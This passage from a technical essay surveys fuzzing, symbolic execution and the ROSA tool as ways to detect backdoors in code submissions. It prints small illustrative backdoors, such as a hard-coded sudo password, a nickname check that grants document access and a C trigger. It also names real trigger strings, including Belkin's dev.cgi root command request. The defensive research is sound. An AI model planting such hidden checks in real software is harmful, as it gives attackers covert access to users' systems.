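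AFL++ can instead record the last few blocks before each step, so that new combinations of blocks also count as progress. It records at most 16 blocks, so it would miss combinations of conditions that lie far apart in the program. Recording entire paths would catch them all, but 12 yes-or-no branches make 4,096 paths and 30 make over a billion. AFL records edges to avoid tracking so many paths.

Anyone who reads the code can still see all four triggers. The last is probably the easiest to disguise, since a server might have good reasons to count features of a request.

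### Steering towards the lines a commit changed

A project checking a submission has little reason to explore the whole program equally. Even accidental bugs are most likely to be in recent changes. *Raise or Check?* (2026) cites a study by Zhu and colleagues, which found that 77% of 23,000 OSS-Fuzz bugs were regressions from recent code changes.

*Directed Greybox Fuzzing*, by Böhme, Pham and colleagues, presents AFLGo, a fuzzer that targets chosen lines of code. A tester gives it a list of files and line numbers, such as the lines a commit changed, and AFLGo spends most of its time trying to reach them.

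Suppose a changed line runs only if a number *n* in the input is greater than 42. Directed fuzzers use three main methods to reach such a target. AFLGo measures how close each run came to the target, in steps through the program, and spends more time on the inputs that came closest. Other fuzzers stop a run as soon as it enters code from which it can no longer reach the target. Still others compare inputs that reached the target with those that didn't, infer that *n* must exceed 42, and favour mutations that keep *n* above 42.

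For an explicit trigger check, however, distance is often the wrong measure. Every password given to the backdoored sudo reaches the planted comparison, one step from the planted assignment, so all wrong passwords are equally close. The fuzzer lacks the right value, which splitting or copying can supply. Directing the search helps more when the check is deep in a part of the program that ordinary inputs seldom reach.

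The best current evidence suggests that directed fuzzing generally doesn't improve on undirected fuzzing. In *LIBAFLGO*, Geretto, Jemmett and colleagues (2025) rebuilt several directed methods on LibAFL, a modern fuzzing framework, so that they all had the same up-to-date components. AFLGo's original methods did better than the newer ones, but across the benchmarks as a whole, none of the directed methods matched plain LibAFL, which had no target.

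Geretto and colleagues give several reasons why earlier papers looked more promising. Most directed fuzzers build on AFL or AFLGo, neither of which has had significant updates for years, and many lack CmpLog. A method that saves runs looks good on a slow fuzzer, but on a fast one its overhead can take more time than the saved runs would have. Many papers also left out the time needed to analyse and recompile the program for each new target. This omission is especially serious for submissions, because each commit changes different lines and so needs another build. In *Evaluating Directed Fuzzers*, Kim, Choi and colleagues ran experiments that used 30 CPU-years and also found common pitfalls in how researchers test these tools.

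These comparisons concern ordinary bugs, so a directed fuzzer could still do better on backdoors. But teams with strong incentives to find bugs in code changes have mostly not relied on directed fuzzing. Some tasks in the AI Cyber Challenge, a competition run by the US defence research agency DARPA, gave teams a code change and asked them to find the bugs it introduced (*ATLANTIS*, 2025). *SoK* (2026), a review of the competition, lists custom directed fuzzing in only two of the seven finalists' systems, but parallel fuzzing in all seven.

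Other ways of using the changed lines take less computation. *FuzzingBrain V2* (2026) describes a system that picks out the changed functions execution can reach and concentrates its analysis on them. The system also has a language model write seeds for the code under study, so the fuzzer can start close to its target. A simpler approach would be to collect every string and number that a commit adds and give them to the fuzzer as a dictionary, a list of values to insert into inputs. For PHP, this list would have included "zerodium". This approach would take almost no computation, but it would miss any value that the program computes while running.

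### What the harness and seeds make possible

No search method can reach code that the harness never calls. If the harness only reads PNG files, the fuzzer won't find a backdoor in the code that writes them, however long it runs. The fuzzer also can't vary any input that the harness keeps fixed. For example, if a harness for sudo varies the password but always runs the same command as the same user, the fuzzer could find a backdoor that opens for the password "let_me_in", but not one that requires a different username.

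Writing a harness takes from a few minutes to several hours, according to Geretto and colleagues. It is quick for a program that reads a file and slow for a single function that needs complicated data, so projects begin with the easy parts. If a backdoor were on a randomly chosen changed line, a harness with the average reach that Kokkonis and colleagues measured would have at most about a one in three chance of triggering it, even with unlimited time. An attacker can reduce that chance by reading an open-source project's harnesses, which are as public as its tests, and putting the backdoor where they don't reach.

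Seeds matter less in principle, because a fuzzer can generate what they lack. Aschermann and colleagues started REDQUEEN with only a string of printable characters, and it covered more code than the other fuzzers they tested on all eight file-processing tools. But a fuzzer that has to discover the input format may run out of time before it reaches the trigger. Kokkonis and colleagues' fuzzer triggered a backdoor in a Belkin router only after they replaced the standard web requests it started from with bare ones aimed at the code that reads web addresses.

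The tester can check some of this in the coverage record before trusting the search. If no run executed the new comparison, the harness or the seeds need work, and more fuzzing probably won't help. If runs reached the comparison but never the code it guards, the tester can check whether splitting or copying should have solved the condition.

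## Solving for the trigger with symbolic execution

A fuzzer can get stuck at a comparison even when every run reaches it. This program runs its payload for exactly one number:

```c
uint32_t x = read_number();
if (x > 1000)
    if (x * 7 + 3 == 24692)
        run_payload();
```

A random guess at a 32-bit number succeeds once in about 4.3 billion tries. Copying 24692 into the input, as CmpLog would, doesn't work because the program compares 24692 with 7*x* + 3, not *x*. Splitting the comparison into bytes would probably work here, since multiplying by seven scrambles the number only a little, but it helps less as the arithmetic gets more complex.

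Subtracting 3 and then dividing by 7 gives *x* = 3527. Symbolic execution automates this kind of reasoning. It runs the program on unknowns instead of values, records the conditions for taking each branch, and solves them to find an input that reaches a chosen point.

### One unknown and three paths

At the first `if`, the unknown *x* could be above 1000 or not, so the symbolic execution engine follows both possibilities and records a condition for each. Such a condition is a constraint. The second `if` splits one of the two paths again, which makes three:

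- *x* ≤ 1000, and the program ends.
- *x* > 1000 and 7*x* + 3 ≠ 24692, and the program ends.
- *x* > 1000 and 7*x* + 3 = 24692, and the payload runs.

The engine passes the constraints for each path to a constraint solver, a program that looks for values that satisfy all of them. For the path to the payload, the solver returns 3527 almost immediately. The tester can then run the program normally on 3527 and watch what happens.

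The solver has to use the computer's arithmetic, in which 32-bit numbers wrap around to zero after 4,294,967,295. If the check were `x * 8 + 4 == 24692`, eight numbers would pass, starting at 3086 and spaced 536,870,912 apart. The solver would normally return only one of them.

Sometimes the solver shows that no solution exists. If the first check were `x > 5000`, no number could pass both checks and the payload could never run, which even a year of fuzzing couldn't establish. The solver can also run out of time or memory before determining whether a solution exists.

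### Why the number of paths explodes

A program with *n* independent branches has up to 2^*n* paths, and a loop can produce a great many branches from very little code:

```c
for (int i = 0; i < 40; i++)
    if (input[i] == ' ')
        spaces++;
```

The loop only counts spaces, but each character is either a space or something else, so each round doubles the number of paths. There are about a million paths after 20 characters and 1.1 trillion after 40. An engine that explored 1,000 paths a second would need about 35 years to cover the 1.1 trillion. This growth is called path explosion.

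An engine can avoid some of the path explosion by merging paths. It keeps one formula in which `spaces` is the sum of forty unknown zeros and ones, instead of following every combination. This formula is harder to solve. In *Driller*, Stephens, Grosen and colleagues (2016) think that merging only delays the explosion.

Within these limits, a solver can handle some triggers that give a fuzzer no useful feedback. For the web server that runs its payload when a request meets twelve common conditions, the engine can go through all the combinations, and the constraints on the one that triggers the payload specify what the request must contain. A solver can also match an ordinary checksum such as CRC-32, because four suitably chosen bytes can bring it to any value, but it can't reverse a cryptographic hash.

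### Concolic execution and Driller

Concolic execution (from "concrete" and "symbolic") starts from a real run. Suppose the program at the beginning of this section runs on 5000. It behaves normally while the engine records the two constraints that 5000 satisfied, *x* > 1000 and 7*x* + 3 ≠ 24692. The engine keeps the first constraint, reverses the second, and gives both to the solver, which returns 3527. The program then runs on 3527, and the engine looks for further branches to flip.

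Because the program actually runs, the engine can use a file's real contents or a server's real reply instead of guessing them. Path explosion is still a problem, since a single run may pass thousands of branches and each flipped branch leads to a new run with more branches to flip.

Stephens and colleagues therefore left most of the exploring to a fuzzer. They noticed that programs accept a wide range of values for some inputs, such as a user's name, and only a few for others, such as the name of a command. A fuzzer handles the first kind well but gets stuck on the second. Driller runs the fuzzer AFL until it stops making progress, then replays the inputs AFL has saved and uses a solver to find new inputs that take branches no run has taken. AFL continues from those. In the paper's simplest example, a program checks for a number whose square is 152,399,025. Random guesses keep missing it,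 but a solver can calculate that the number is 12,345.

The Driller paper tested its tool on 126 programs from the qualifying round of the Cyber Grand Challenge, an earlier DARPA competition for automated bug-finding. Driller found as many vulnerabilities as the top-scoring team had in the same amount of time. The solver contributed modestly to this result, producing useful new inputs for 13 of the 41 programs on which AFL got stuck. The 2016 version of AFL also had no CmpLog. Many of the fixed values and command names that stopped it would not stop AFL++ today, so adding a solver probably helps less now.

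Constraint solving also takes a lot of computation. Partly for this reason, Vinçont, Bardin and Marcozzi proposed a lighter form of symbolic execution in *A Tight Integration of Symbolic Execution and Fuzzing*.

### Dates and commands in malware

A worm that attacks only on certain dates does nothing suspicious when a malware analyst runs it on any other day. In *Automatically Identifying Trigger-based Behavior in Malware*, Brumley, Hartwig and colleagues (2007) built MineSweeper to find those dates.

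The analyst first tells MineSweeper where the trigger might come from, such as the system clock, the keyboard or the network. (MineSweeper can suggest candidates by listing the calls the program makes.) It then treats whatever those sources return as unknown and runs everything else normally. In their worked example, a worm asks Windows for the time and checks four parts of the answer. The path to the attack has these constraints:

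day = 9 ∧ hour = 10 ∧ month = 11 ∧ minute = 6

MineSweeper solves the trigger constraints and runs the worm again in a controlled environment. When the worm requests the time, MineSweeper returns 10:06 on 9 November, and the worm attacks.

Brumley and colleagues tried MineSweeper on four real programs. It found in nine minutes that the email worm NetSky attacked on 26 February 2004 between 6 and 9 in the morning. It took 28 minutes to find two attack dates for another worm, MyDoom, and the date on which that worm stopped spreading. It also recovered the commands that controlled the attack tool TFN. In every case, fewer than one instruction in 19,000 involved an unknown value, which kept the formulas small.

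The fourth program, a commercial keylogger, started recording when a window's title contained a chosen word. It looked for the word with `strstr`, a standard function that searches one string for another. MineSweeper branched on character after character inside that function and made very slow progress. After Brumley and colleagues replaced `strstr` with a short hand-written summary of its effect, MineSweeper found the word in about two minutes.

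These tests favoured the method, because antivirus researchers had already published the worms' dates and the analyst knew from the start that the programs were worth investigating. Legitimate software also often behaves differently depending on the date or a command. *Towards Semi-automated Detection of Trigger-based Behavior for Software Security Assurance* (2017) applies the same mixture of concrete and symbolic execution to source code, which is closer to reviewing a submission. It produces suspicious test cases that a person still has to investigate.

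### Firmalice and the input anyone could work out

*Firmalice* (Shoshitaishvili, Wang and colleagues, 2015) looks for ways around the login in device firmware. An analyst first writes a security policy that names something the device should do only for logged-in users. For a simple device, the policy might forbid showing the prompt "Command:" to anyone who hasn't logged in.

Firmalice finds the code that prints the prompt, discards code that can't affect whether execution gets there, and runs the rest symbolically. In their example, the login function accepts the stored username and password, but also accepts "GO" and "ON". Two paths therefore reach the prompt:

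| Path | Username must equal | Password must equal |
|---|---|---|
| Backdoor | "GO" | "ON" |
| Normal login | the stored username | the stored password |

Firmalice reports a bypass when the solver finds that exactly one input satisfies the constraints on a path. Anyone with a copy of the firmware can work out a backdoor's input, but the normal login path checks a stored username and password that differ from device to device, so its constraints allow many inputs.

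This gives Firmalice a way to recognize a backdoor as well as search for one. On the backdoored sudo, the same test should pick out "let_me_in", because that path has one fixed solution while the legitimate path depends on the user's real password. But an attacker can evade the test by writing a backdoor that accepts more than one value. Shoshitaishvili and colleagues describe one that accepts any number divisible by 10, which Firmalice would treat as a normal login. They hadn't seen such a backdoor in practice, though one would be easy to write.

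Firmalice's developers tested it on three devices in which other researchers had already reported backdoors. It found a fixed username and password in a security camera in 31 minutes. In a Dell printer it found a special network message that gave administrator access, but this took about 12 hours, even though Firmalice had narrowed the search from 151,005 basic blocks to 532.

Firmalice found nothing in the third device, an electricity meter. Shoshitaishvili and colleagues assumed that it had missed the backdoor, so they studied the code by hand and tried the attack on a real meter. The secret credentials worked only for someone who had already logged in with valid ones. The researcher who wrote the original report confirmed that Shoshitaishvili's team had misunderstood it.

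Firmalice was tested on only three devices, partly because someone had to write a policy for each one. The input it reports may also fail on the device, because the discarded code can impose further requirements. When Kokkonis and colleagues looked for earlier backdoor detectors to compare with theirs, they could not find a working version of Firmalice.

### Narrow conditions in Android apps

Fratantonio, Bianchi and colleagues published *TriggerScope* a year after Firmalice. They tried to detect logic bombs (harmful behaviour that starts only under particular circumstances) without a separate policy for every program. They reasoned that a logic bomb needs an unusually narrow condition, whatever it does afterwards. TriggerScope analyses an Android app's code symbolically, without running the app, to find places where the code compares the time, the phone's location or a text message with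 a fixed value. It then checks whether the comparison controls a sensitive operation, such as connecting to the internet.

It flagged all 14 malicious apps in the test, 11 of which an outside team had written to resemble state-sponsored malware. It also flagged 35 (0.38%) of 9,313 apps from Google's store that were assumed to be benign. Most of the 35 used narrow conditions for harmless purposes. One, for example, displayed "Welcome to Yamagata Station!" when the phone was at that station in Japan.

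But two of the 35 contained something like a backdoor. One app let owners unlock their phones by sending a text message with a keyword they had chosen, but it also accepted a long string of letters written into the code. The other replied with the phone's location to anyone who sent it "MPS: gps". TriggerScope's output included the required text for both, so Fratantonio and colleagues could send the messages to a real phone and confirm that they worked.

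A later study did not reproduce TriggerScope's low rate of false alarms. The tool wasn't publicly available, so Samhi and Bartel (2021), in *On The (In)Effectiveness of Static Logic Bomb Detection for Android Apps*, rebuilt it from the published description and ran their version on 508,122 apps. It flagged 99,651 of them, and they put the false-positive rate at more than 17%. About 98% of the reported triggers involved time. They could lower the false-positive rate to about 0.3%, but only with drastic measures such as removing 90% of the operations that counted as sensitive, which would make the tool miss many real logic bombs. TriggerScope's creators read the new paper and saw no significant problem with the rebuilt version.

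Narrow conditions are common in honest code. These rates come from apps rather than pull requests, but the gap between them would matter a great deal to a maintainer. Of 500 open pull requests, 0.38% is about two and 17% is 85.

### Recent systems find the target automatically

A person must tell all three systems what to look for. MineSweeper needs the source of the trigger, Firmalice needs a policy, and TriggerScope needs a list of sensitive operations. *Malware MultiVerse* (2021) still describes automatically choosing where to start and end the analysis as an unsolved challenge for symbolic tools that deal with logic bombs.

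*Through the Authentication Maze* (Zhong, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents AuthSpark, a system that automates this choice for logins. AuthSpark records what a device's web server executes during a successful login and during a failed one. The two records are very similar until the server checks the password, so AuthSpark takes the point where they diverge as the password check. It then follows the result of that check through the program to find code that runs only after a successful login, and uses that code as the target.

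AuthSpark correctly located 42 of 44 such checks in firmware from 32 devices. It detected all 14 known login bypasses in the test set and found six new ones in the latest firmware. One of these bypasses involved no secret value. The server supported two login schemes, and a request that mixed parts of both passed without either checking the password. Zhong and colleagues think Firmalice would have missed this flaw, because it would have found its target by looking for the text "login success", which only one of the schemes prints.

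AuthSpark addresses much the same problem as Firmalice but uses a fuzzer instead of a solver. Symbolic execution is still in use, for example in Atlantis, the system that won DARPA's AI Cyber Challenge in 2025, which combined it with language models, directed fuzzing and static analysis.

A language model can also do the solver's job. In *Program Analysis Guided LLM Agent for Proof-of-Concept Generation*, Desai, Shafiuzzaman and colleagues (2026) give a model a line of code that may be vulnerable and a chain of function calls that leads to it. The model proposes an input, and if the program doesn't crash, the model is told which code ran and tries again. With the open-weight model DeepSeek 3.2, this worked for 64.6% of 203 known vulnerabilities. Desai and colleagues suggest using the lines changed by each commit as targets, so that a person doesn't have to choose them. However, their system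 stops when the program crashes, and a well-made backdoor doesn't crash it.

### Solving for the trigger in a submission

Symbolic execution is much easier on a small commit than on a whole program. To check the backdoored sudo, an engine could start at `verify_user`, the function the attacker changed, and treat both the password and the result of the real check as unknown. The planted `if` would be the only branch, and the solver would return "let_me_in" immediately. The tester would then have to run the whole program on that password, because an input that works on one function may be impossible to deliver from outside. This is easy for sudo, but for a function deep inside a database, the engine may have to search for a path from the program's real input to that function, which brings back the problem of path explosion.

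Programs also depend on files, networks and the operating system. Real sudo reads a configuration file and looks up the user's account before it allows or refuses a command. An engine that treats all of this as unknown can produce situations that never occur, while one that uses the real files will miss a trigger that needs a different configuration. The usual compromise is to write summaries of the outside calls by hand. Shoshitaishvili and colleagues summarized 49 standard C functions and accepted that Firmalice would miss a backdoor hidden inside any of those functions. A project could reuse its summaries across submissions, but somebody would have to write them and keep them correct.

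Strings cause trouble even when the trigger is simple. They can cause the branching that slowed MineSweeper down, and an engine often has to assume a maximum input length. If that limit is ten characters, the engine will report that no input can trigger the ProFTPD backdoor, because "HELP ACIDBITCHEZ" has sixteen.

A solver has to reproduce exactly how computers round decimal numbers, which makes its formulas much larger and slower to solve. For example, by ordinary algebra the check `x * 0.1 == 0.3` is satisfied when *x* is 3. In standard double-precision arithmetic, however, 3 × 0.1 comes out as 0.30000000000000004, so 3 fails the check, while 2.9999999999999996 passes. An attacker could put a few such calculations in front of a trigger in scientific or graphics code, where they would look normal.

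The most basic difficulty is deciding what the solver should look for. A commit's changed lines show which code to reach, but nearly every commit adds branches, and the solver could find inputs that reach most of them. For the Linux backdoor, it would find the right combination of flags immediately, but its answer would not show that the caller had become root.

A project can supply the missing target by stating what must never happen. For sudo, the rule might be that it never runs a command unless `ctx->verify` has returned success. The solver would then return "let_me_in" as an input that breaks this rule. Shoshitaishvili and colleagues needed a new policy for each device, but a project could write a rule like this once and apply it to every later submission.

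## Recognising that a backdoor has fired

A solver can search for an input that breaks a rule such as "sudo never runs a command unless `ctx->verify` has returned success", and a fuzzer can check the same rule after every run. Few projects have written such rules down. Without one, a fuzzer checks each run only for a crash or new coverage, so it can run an input that triggers the backdoor, find neither, and discard the input.

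This happens more easily than the sudo example suggests. Suppose an online shop keeps its discount codes in a table, and an attacker adds a row that takes 99% off. The program looks up the secret code the same way as a genuine one, so it crosses the same edges. A fuzzer that guessed the secret code would discard it as a repeat of an earlier run.

In *The Oracle Problem in Software Testing*, Barr, Harman and colleagues define the oracle problem as distinguishing a program's correct behaviour on a given input from potentially incorrect behaviour. Unless that judgement is automated, a person has to make it for every run, which is impossible at 10,000 runs a second.

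### Crashes, stated rules and pairs of runs

Fuzzers look for crashes by default because a crash is a fault in almost any program. A stated property, like the rule for sudo, is more precise, but someone has to write it for each program. HumIDIFy, an older tool that Kokkonis and colleagues review, reduces this work by using one list of expected features for all programs that implement the same network protocol. It guesses which protocol a program implements and checks the program against that protocol's list. A list for web servers might say that they use TCP and never UDP. That rule would expose a web server that secretly listened for UDP messages, but a hard-coded password would go unnoticed because checking passwords is normal for a web server.

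A metamorphic oracle checks a relation between the results of two inputs, so a tester can find a fault without knowing the correct result for either. For example, sin(1.3) must equal sin(π − 1.3). If a program returns clearly different values for the two, at least one is wrong.

sudo has a similar relation: any two wrong passwords should have the same effect. If the real password is strong and nobody gives it to the fuzzer, practically every password the fuzzer generates is wrong, and sudo should refuse them all. "let_me_in" stands out because sudo runs the command.

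### How ROSA chooses what to compare

Kokkonis and colleagues turned this idea into ROSA, a tool that adds a metamorphic oracle to AFL++. The oracle checks that inputs a program should handle alike produce the same types of system call.

It is hard to know which inputs the program should handle alike. If only the password varies, all wrong passwords belong together. But a real sudo command also names a user and a program to run, and can include many option flags. These combine in too many ways to sort into groups by hand. ROSA approximates the groups from coverage, on the assumption that two inputs that take nearly the same route through a program should probably be handled alike.

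ROSA begins with a collection phase of about one minute. AFL++ fuzzes the program, and ROSA keeps the inputs that cover new combinations of edges as representatives of normal behaviour. For each of these inputs, it also records a system-call profile, which lists the types of request the program made to the operating system. A profile shows that the program opened a file, but not which file or how many times.

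A detection phase of several hours follows. For each new input, ROSA finds the representative with the closest coverage and reports any difference between their two profiles.

ROSA measures closeness by Hamming distance, the number of positions at which two lists differ. In a small example from the original ROSA paper, the program has four edges and can make three types of system call (1 means that the run included the edge or call):

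| Input | Edge 1 | Edge 2 | Edge 3 | Edge 4 | `read` | `kill` | `open` |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| New input | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 | 0 | 1 |
| Representative A | 1 | 0 | 1 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 1 |
| Representative B | 0 | 1 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The new input differs from A at edges 2 and 4, a distance of two. It differs from B at edges 1, 3 and 4, a distance of three. ROSA therefore compares the new input with A. Their profiles differ in one place, because the new input caused a `read` and A did not, so ROSA reports it. Had A and B been equally close, ROSA would have reported the input only if its profile differed from both. (The tool's Kokkonis and colleagues have since made minor corrections to how it selects representatives, so the current version may differ in detail.)

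On sudo, the collection phase might save "test" and "testtttttttt". When the fuzzer later tries "test" followed by a line break and more letters, the coverage changes slightly but the system calls do not, so ROSA accepts the input as safe. The password "let_me_in" is closest to "testtttttttt", but it makes sudo start a new process and execute the requested command. ROSA reports the password and the extra system calls.

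One backdoor can produce hundreds of slightly different triggering inputs. ROSA reports each difference from a given representative only once, which cut the number of reports about tenfold in the experiments.

If the collection phase is too short, ROSA misses some normal behaviour and later reports it as suspicious. If it is too long, the fuzzer may trigger the backdoor during collection, and the triggering input becomes a representative of normal behaviour. Kokkonis and colleagues tried lengths from 30 seconds to 20 minutes. The longer phases produced fewer reports to check but missed the backdoor more often, although even the worst setting found it in 72% of runs.

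With the chosen collection phase of one minute, a triggering input was among the representatives in about one run in 18. This never prevented detection, because the same backdoor usually works with many kinds of input. The sudo password, for example, works with any combination of flags, and the collection phase is unlikely to cover them all.

Kokkonis and colleagues chose the one-minute setting using the same backdoors on which they then evaluated ROSA, which may slightly inflate the results. In the 2025 paper, they describe every phase length they tried as acceptable, but in later work they write that a user must calibrate the phase carefully for each program, fuzzer set-up and machine.

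### The 17 backdoors in ROSARUM

To test ROSA, Kokkonis and colleagues assembled ROSARUM, a benchmark of 17 programs with one backdoor each. Seven of the backdoors are authentic. Three are the PHP, ProFTPD and vsFTPd backdoors, and four come from routers made by Belkin, D-Link, Linksys and Tenda.

The team struggled to obtain even seven real backdoors. They followed up 15 reports, but could not get samples for four, and two more would not run outside their original devices. They also left out the TRENDnet backdoor, which turned out to be harmless, and xz, because only the attacker can produce the signature that triggers it.

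The other ten are synthetic. One is the "let_me_in" password in sudo. A researcher who had not worked on ROSA planted the remaining nine in widely used open-source software, including the image library libpng and the database SQLite. ROSA's developers then ran the tool without knowing how these nine backdoors worked, which makes it less likely that they had tailored it to them.

Each backdoor had ten runs of up to eight hours on eight processor cores, and Belkin had ten more with different seeds. ROSA found the backdoor in 156 of the 180 runs (87%) and took about an hour and a half on average. The average for a single backdoor ranged from 90 seconds for the Linksys router to five hours for libsndfile, a sound library. Emulation took up much of this time. ROSA has to work on router software whose source code is unavailable, so it runs the program in an emulator that records each edge and system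 call.

For each program, ROSARUM includes a second copy that prints a marker whenever an input meets the trigger condition. Kokkonis and colleagues used these copies to establish that all 24 failures occurred because the fuzzer never generated an input that met the condition.

A person had to check an estimated seven or so reported inputs per run, at roughly two minutes each. For a successful run, this estimate is the number of reports someone would have to pick at random to have a 95% chance of including a real trigger. SQLite needed the most checking, with 26 inputs on average, or nearly an hour, while sudo needed one input. Without ROSA's oracle, the reviewer of an average SQLite run would have had 4,705 saved seeds to check.

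These figures are less informative about clean software, which is what a reviewer has nearly all the time. The best hint comes from the ten Belkin runs with standard seeds. None of them triggered the backdoor, so all their reports, an average of four per run, were false alarms. Eight minutes of checking per run is reasonable when auditing a router before a company buys thousands of them, but a project with 50 submissions a day would need nearly seven hours of checking daily, plus computing time. In *Bringing automatic detection of backdoors to the CI pipeline*, Marcozzi and Kokkonis accept that ROSA's false alarms and the computing time it can need are a serious problem for such projects. They responded with Lily, a tool that compares each submission with the version before it.

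### The Belkin router

Belkin's F9K1102 router runs a web server based on the open-source program Boa. Belkin's version contains an extra address, `dev.cgi`, which takes a command from the request and executes it as root without requiring a login.

The server handles an ordinary request such as `GET /` by reading it and writing a reply. A request for `/dev.cgi?c=foo` also makes the server create a process and execute `/bin/sh`, which adds two types of call to the profile. Once the fuzzer generates this request, ROSA recognises it easily. In a live demonstration at FOSDEM, a conference for open-source developers, the presenters sent the server the same kind of request with the command `id`, and the reply showed that they were root. They had biased the fuzzer to find the address quickly, because a normal search takes about four hours.

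Finding the trigger was the hard part. The fuzzer failed in all ten runs with the standard seeds but succeeded in seven of ten when it started from bare GET requests. Kokkonis and colleagues chose those requests because an address is a convenient place to hide a secret value.

This was a reasonable guess, but the Belkin backdoor was already public. An auditor with an unfamiliar program would not know whether to focus on addresses, headers, cookies or uploaded files, and might need a separate set of seeds for each.

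The headline figures depend on which seeds are used for this case. With only the standard seeds, ROSA found 16 of the 17 backdoors and succeeded in 149 of 170 runs. With the specialised seeds instead, it found all 17 and succeeded in 156 runs. The average of an hour and a half is also based on the specialised seeds.

### What the success rate measures

Most of the backdoors in ROSARUM check explicitly for a trigger, and Kokkonis and colleagues turned on the AFL++ features that get past such checks. The 87% therefore mostly measures how often a fuzzer with those features can get past an explicit check in eight hours. Adding ten failed runs on xz would lower it to 82%, and adding more backdoors with cryptographic triggers would lower it further. Nobody knows how common such triggers are among undiscovered backdoors, so 87% isn't an estimate of the share of all backdoors that ROSA would find.

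The oracle's perfect record also rests on few cases. There were 156 successful runs, but repeated runs on one program mostly test the same payload, so the effective sample size is closer to 17. Even if those 17 were a random sample of all backdoors, an oracle that misses 16% of all backdoors would still have a 5% chance of detecting all 17 (0.84^17 ≈ 0.05).

They are also a sample of easily noticed payloads. Eleven of the 17 open a shell or run the attacker's commands or code, and two others encrypt or delete the user's home directory. An image library that starts a shell behaves very differently from one that decodes an image. I would trust the oracle's record for payloads like these, but not for quieter ones.

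### Stringer reads the strings instead

Only one earlier backdoor detector, Stringer (Thomas, Chothia and Garcia, 2017), still worked well enough for a comparison. It analyses a compiled program without running it. It finds the functions that compare data with fixed strings, works out which strings the data must match to reach each block of code, and scores each string by its influence on the program's path. A string scores highly if matching it is the only way to reach a large part of the program.

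Kokkonis and colleagues ran Stringer on the same benchmark:

| | ROSA | Stringer |
|---|---|---|
| Backdoors found | 17 of 17 (with specialised seeds for Belkin) | 4 of 17 |
| Items to inspect, on average | 7 inputs | 308 strings |
| Typical time to find a backdoor | Minutes to hours | Seconds to minutes |

Stringer was about 1,900 times faster than ROSA on average. It found the ProFTPD word in seven seconds, while ROSA failed to find it in four runs out of ten. But each of Stringer's strings takes more work to check than one of ROSA's inputs, because the reviewer has to locate the string in the compiled program and work out what the surrounding code does. Even at two minutes each, checking 308 strings would take about ten hours.

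Many backdoors don't contain a suspicious string. The altered vsFTPd tests for the colon and the bracket as two separate characters, so there is no ":)" for Stringer to extract. Stringer also missed "let_me_in", even though the source code passes that password directly to `strcmp`.

The comparison is a little unfair to Stringer, which was meant to help people who were already analysing firmware by hand. The documentation for *Strngr*, a rewrite of the tool, presents its ranking as a starting point for manual analysis. A reviewer using it that way could start at the top of the list and stop early.

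Stringer and ROSA could work well together. Stringer succeeded on four programs (PHP, ProFTPD, libpng and libsndfile), and ROSA had at least one failed run on each of them, ten in total. Giving Stringer's strings to the fuzzer as a dictionary would take a few minutes and might have made some of those runs succeed. The reviewer would no longer need to read 308 strings, because the fuzzer would try them and ROSA would report only those that changed the program's behaviour.

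### Must a payload change the system calls?

Kokkonis and colleagues assume that any meaningful backdoor must make system calls, which is sound for an ordinary application. ROSA depends on a stronger assumption, that the payload makes different *types* of system call from those the program makes on a similar innocent input.

The gap matters because a program can use the same `write` call to output a wrong answer as a right one. Even stealing a file may not change the profile. If a web server normally opens a page, reads it and sends it, it can take the same three steps to return its private key from a secret address. The only difference is the file name, which ROSA ignores.

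It ignores file names and output because these also differ between requests for two public pages. An oracle that compared either would report nearly every request, whereas types of call are coarse enough to stay the same across most normal inputs.

Kokkonis and colleagues concede that an attacker could in theory build a payload from the program's usual types of call, but they expect this to be hard in practice. There is some evidence for this, since ROSA detected several payloads in ROSARUM that used only calls common elsewhere in the program. It could do so because it compares each input with its closest match, not with the program as a whole. An attacker who wants a shell will therefore have difficulty avoiding detection, but one who only wants the program to return a different number needs no special effort, because the call profile stays the same by default.

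A backdoor with a more visible payload can also hide by staying inactive when it detects a tracing tool. ROSA doesn't use such a tool while fuzzing, but when an audience member at FOSDEM asked about these backdoors, the speaker accepted that such evasion is a limitation and added that the real backdoors they had studied did not attempt it.

### Oracles for wrong answers

To detect a payload that only returns a wrong answer, a tester needs an oracle with some information about the correct answer. The amount of information needed varies widely, as three invented examples show.

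**A mis-sorted list.** An auction site sorts bids from highest to lowest, but the attacker has changed the function so that a bid with the reference "K-7731" always comes first. Sorting happens entirely in memory, and the site displays the winner with its usual calls, so ROSA would report nothing. The missing rule is easy to write:

```python
result = sort_bids(bids)
assert all(a.amount >= b.amount for a, b in zip(result, result[1:]))
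assert Counter(result) == Counter(bids)
```

The first assertion checks the order. The second checks that the function returned the bids it received, each the right number of times, since otherwise a payload could let the attacker win by deleting rival bids. The assertions still allow equal bids in any order, so the attacker could win every tie. The site can prevent this by also requiring that the earlier of two equal bids comes first.

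In one example, pencils cost £1 and staplers £8, so 17 pencils and three staplers should cost £41, but the planted code charges 41p for exactly that basket. The only general way to calculate the correct price of every basket is to write the pricing code again. A tester can instead check the metamorphic rule that removing an item from a basket should never raise its price. Removing one pencil here raises the price from 41p to £40, which breaks the rule and exposes the payload.

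If the attacker knows about this rule, he can charge £40 for the full basket instead. Removing a pencil then leaves the price unchanged, which the rule allows. He still gets a free pencil, but the rule has reduced his profit from £40.59 to £1. Many useful oracles similarly limit what a payload can do without excluding it altogether.

Legitimate pricing can break the same rule. If the shop takes 20% off orders of £50 or more, a £50 basket costs £40 and a £49 basket costs £49. The tester has to make an exception for that offer, and an attacker can hide a backdoor in each exception. The rule also wouldn't catch the 99% discount code, which lowers every basket's price by the same proportion. Catching that code requires another rule, for example that no code takes off more than 30%, and someone at the shop has to know the limit.

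**A permissive access decision.** This function decides whether a user may read a document:

```python
def may_read(user, doc):
    if user.id == doc.owner_id:
        return True
    if doc.id in user.grants:
        return True
    return user.nickname == "heron-41"
```

The last line of `may_read` should be `return False`. The function is pure, meaning that its result depends only on its arguments and that it does nothing except return that result. If a harness calls it directly, it makes no system calls on any input, so ROSA has no system calls to compare.

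Running the whole server looks more promising, because the server opens and sends a document when it permits a request but only sends an error message when it refuses one. The D-Link and sudo backdoors in ROSARUM also cause wrong access decisions, and ROSA caught both in every run. But ROSA may fail here because of how it chooses representatives.

Suppose every request crosses one edge, a refusal crosses one more, and a request that sends a document crosses four different ones. The planted test adds another edge when it succeeds. The triggering request then differs from a legitimate permitted request by one edge and from a refusal by six. ROSA therefore compares it with the permitted request, finds the same types of system call, and classifies it as safe.

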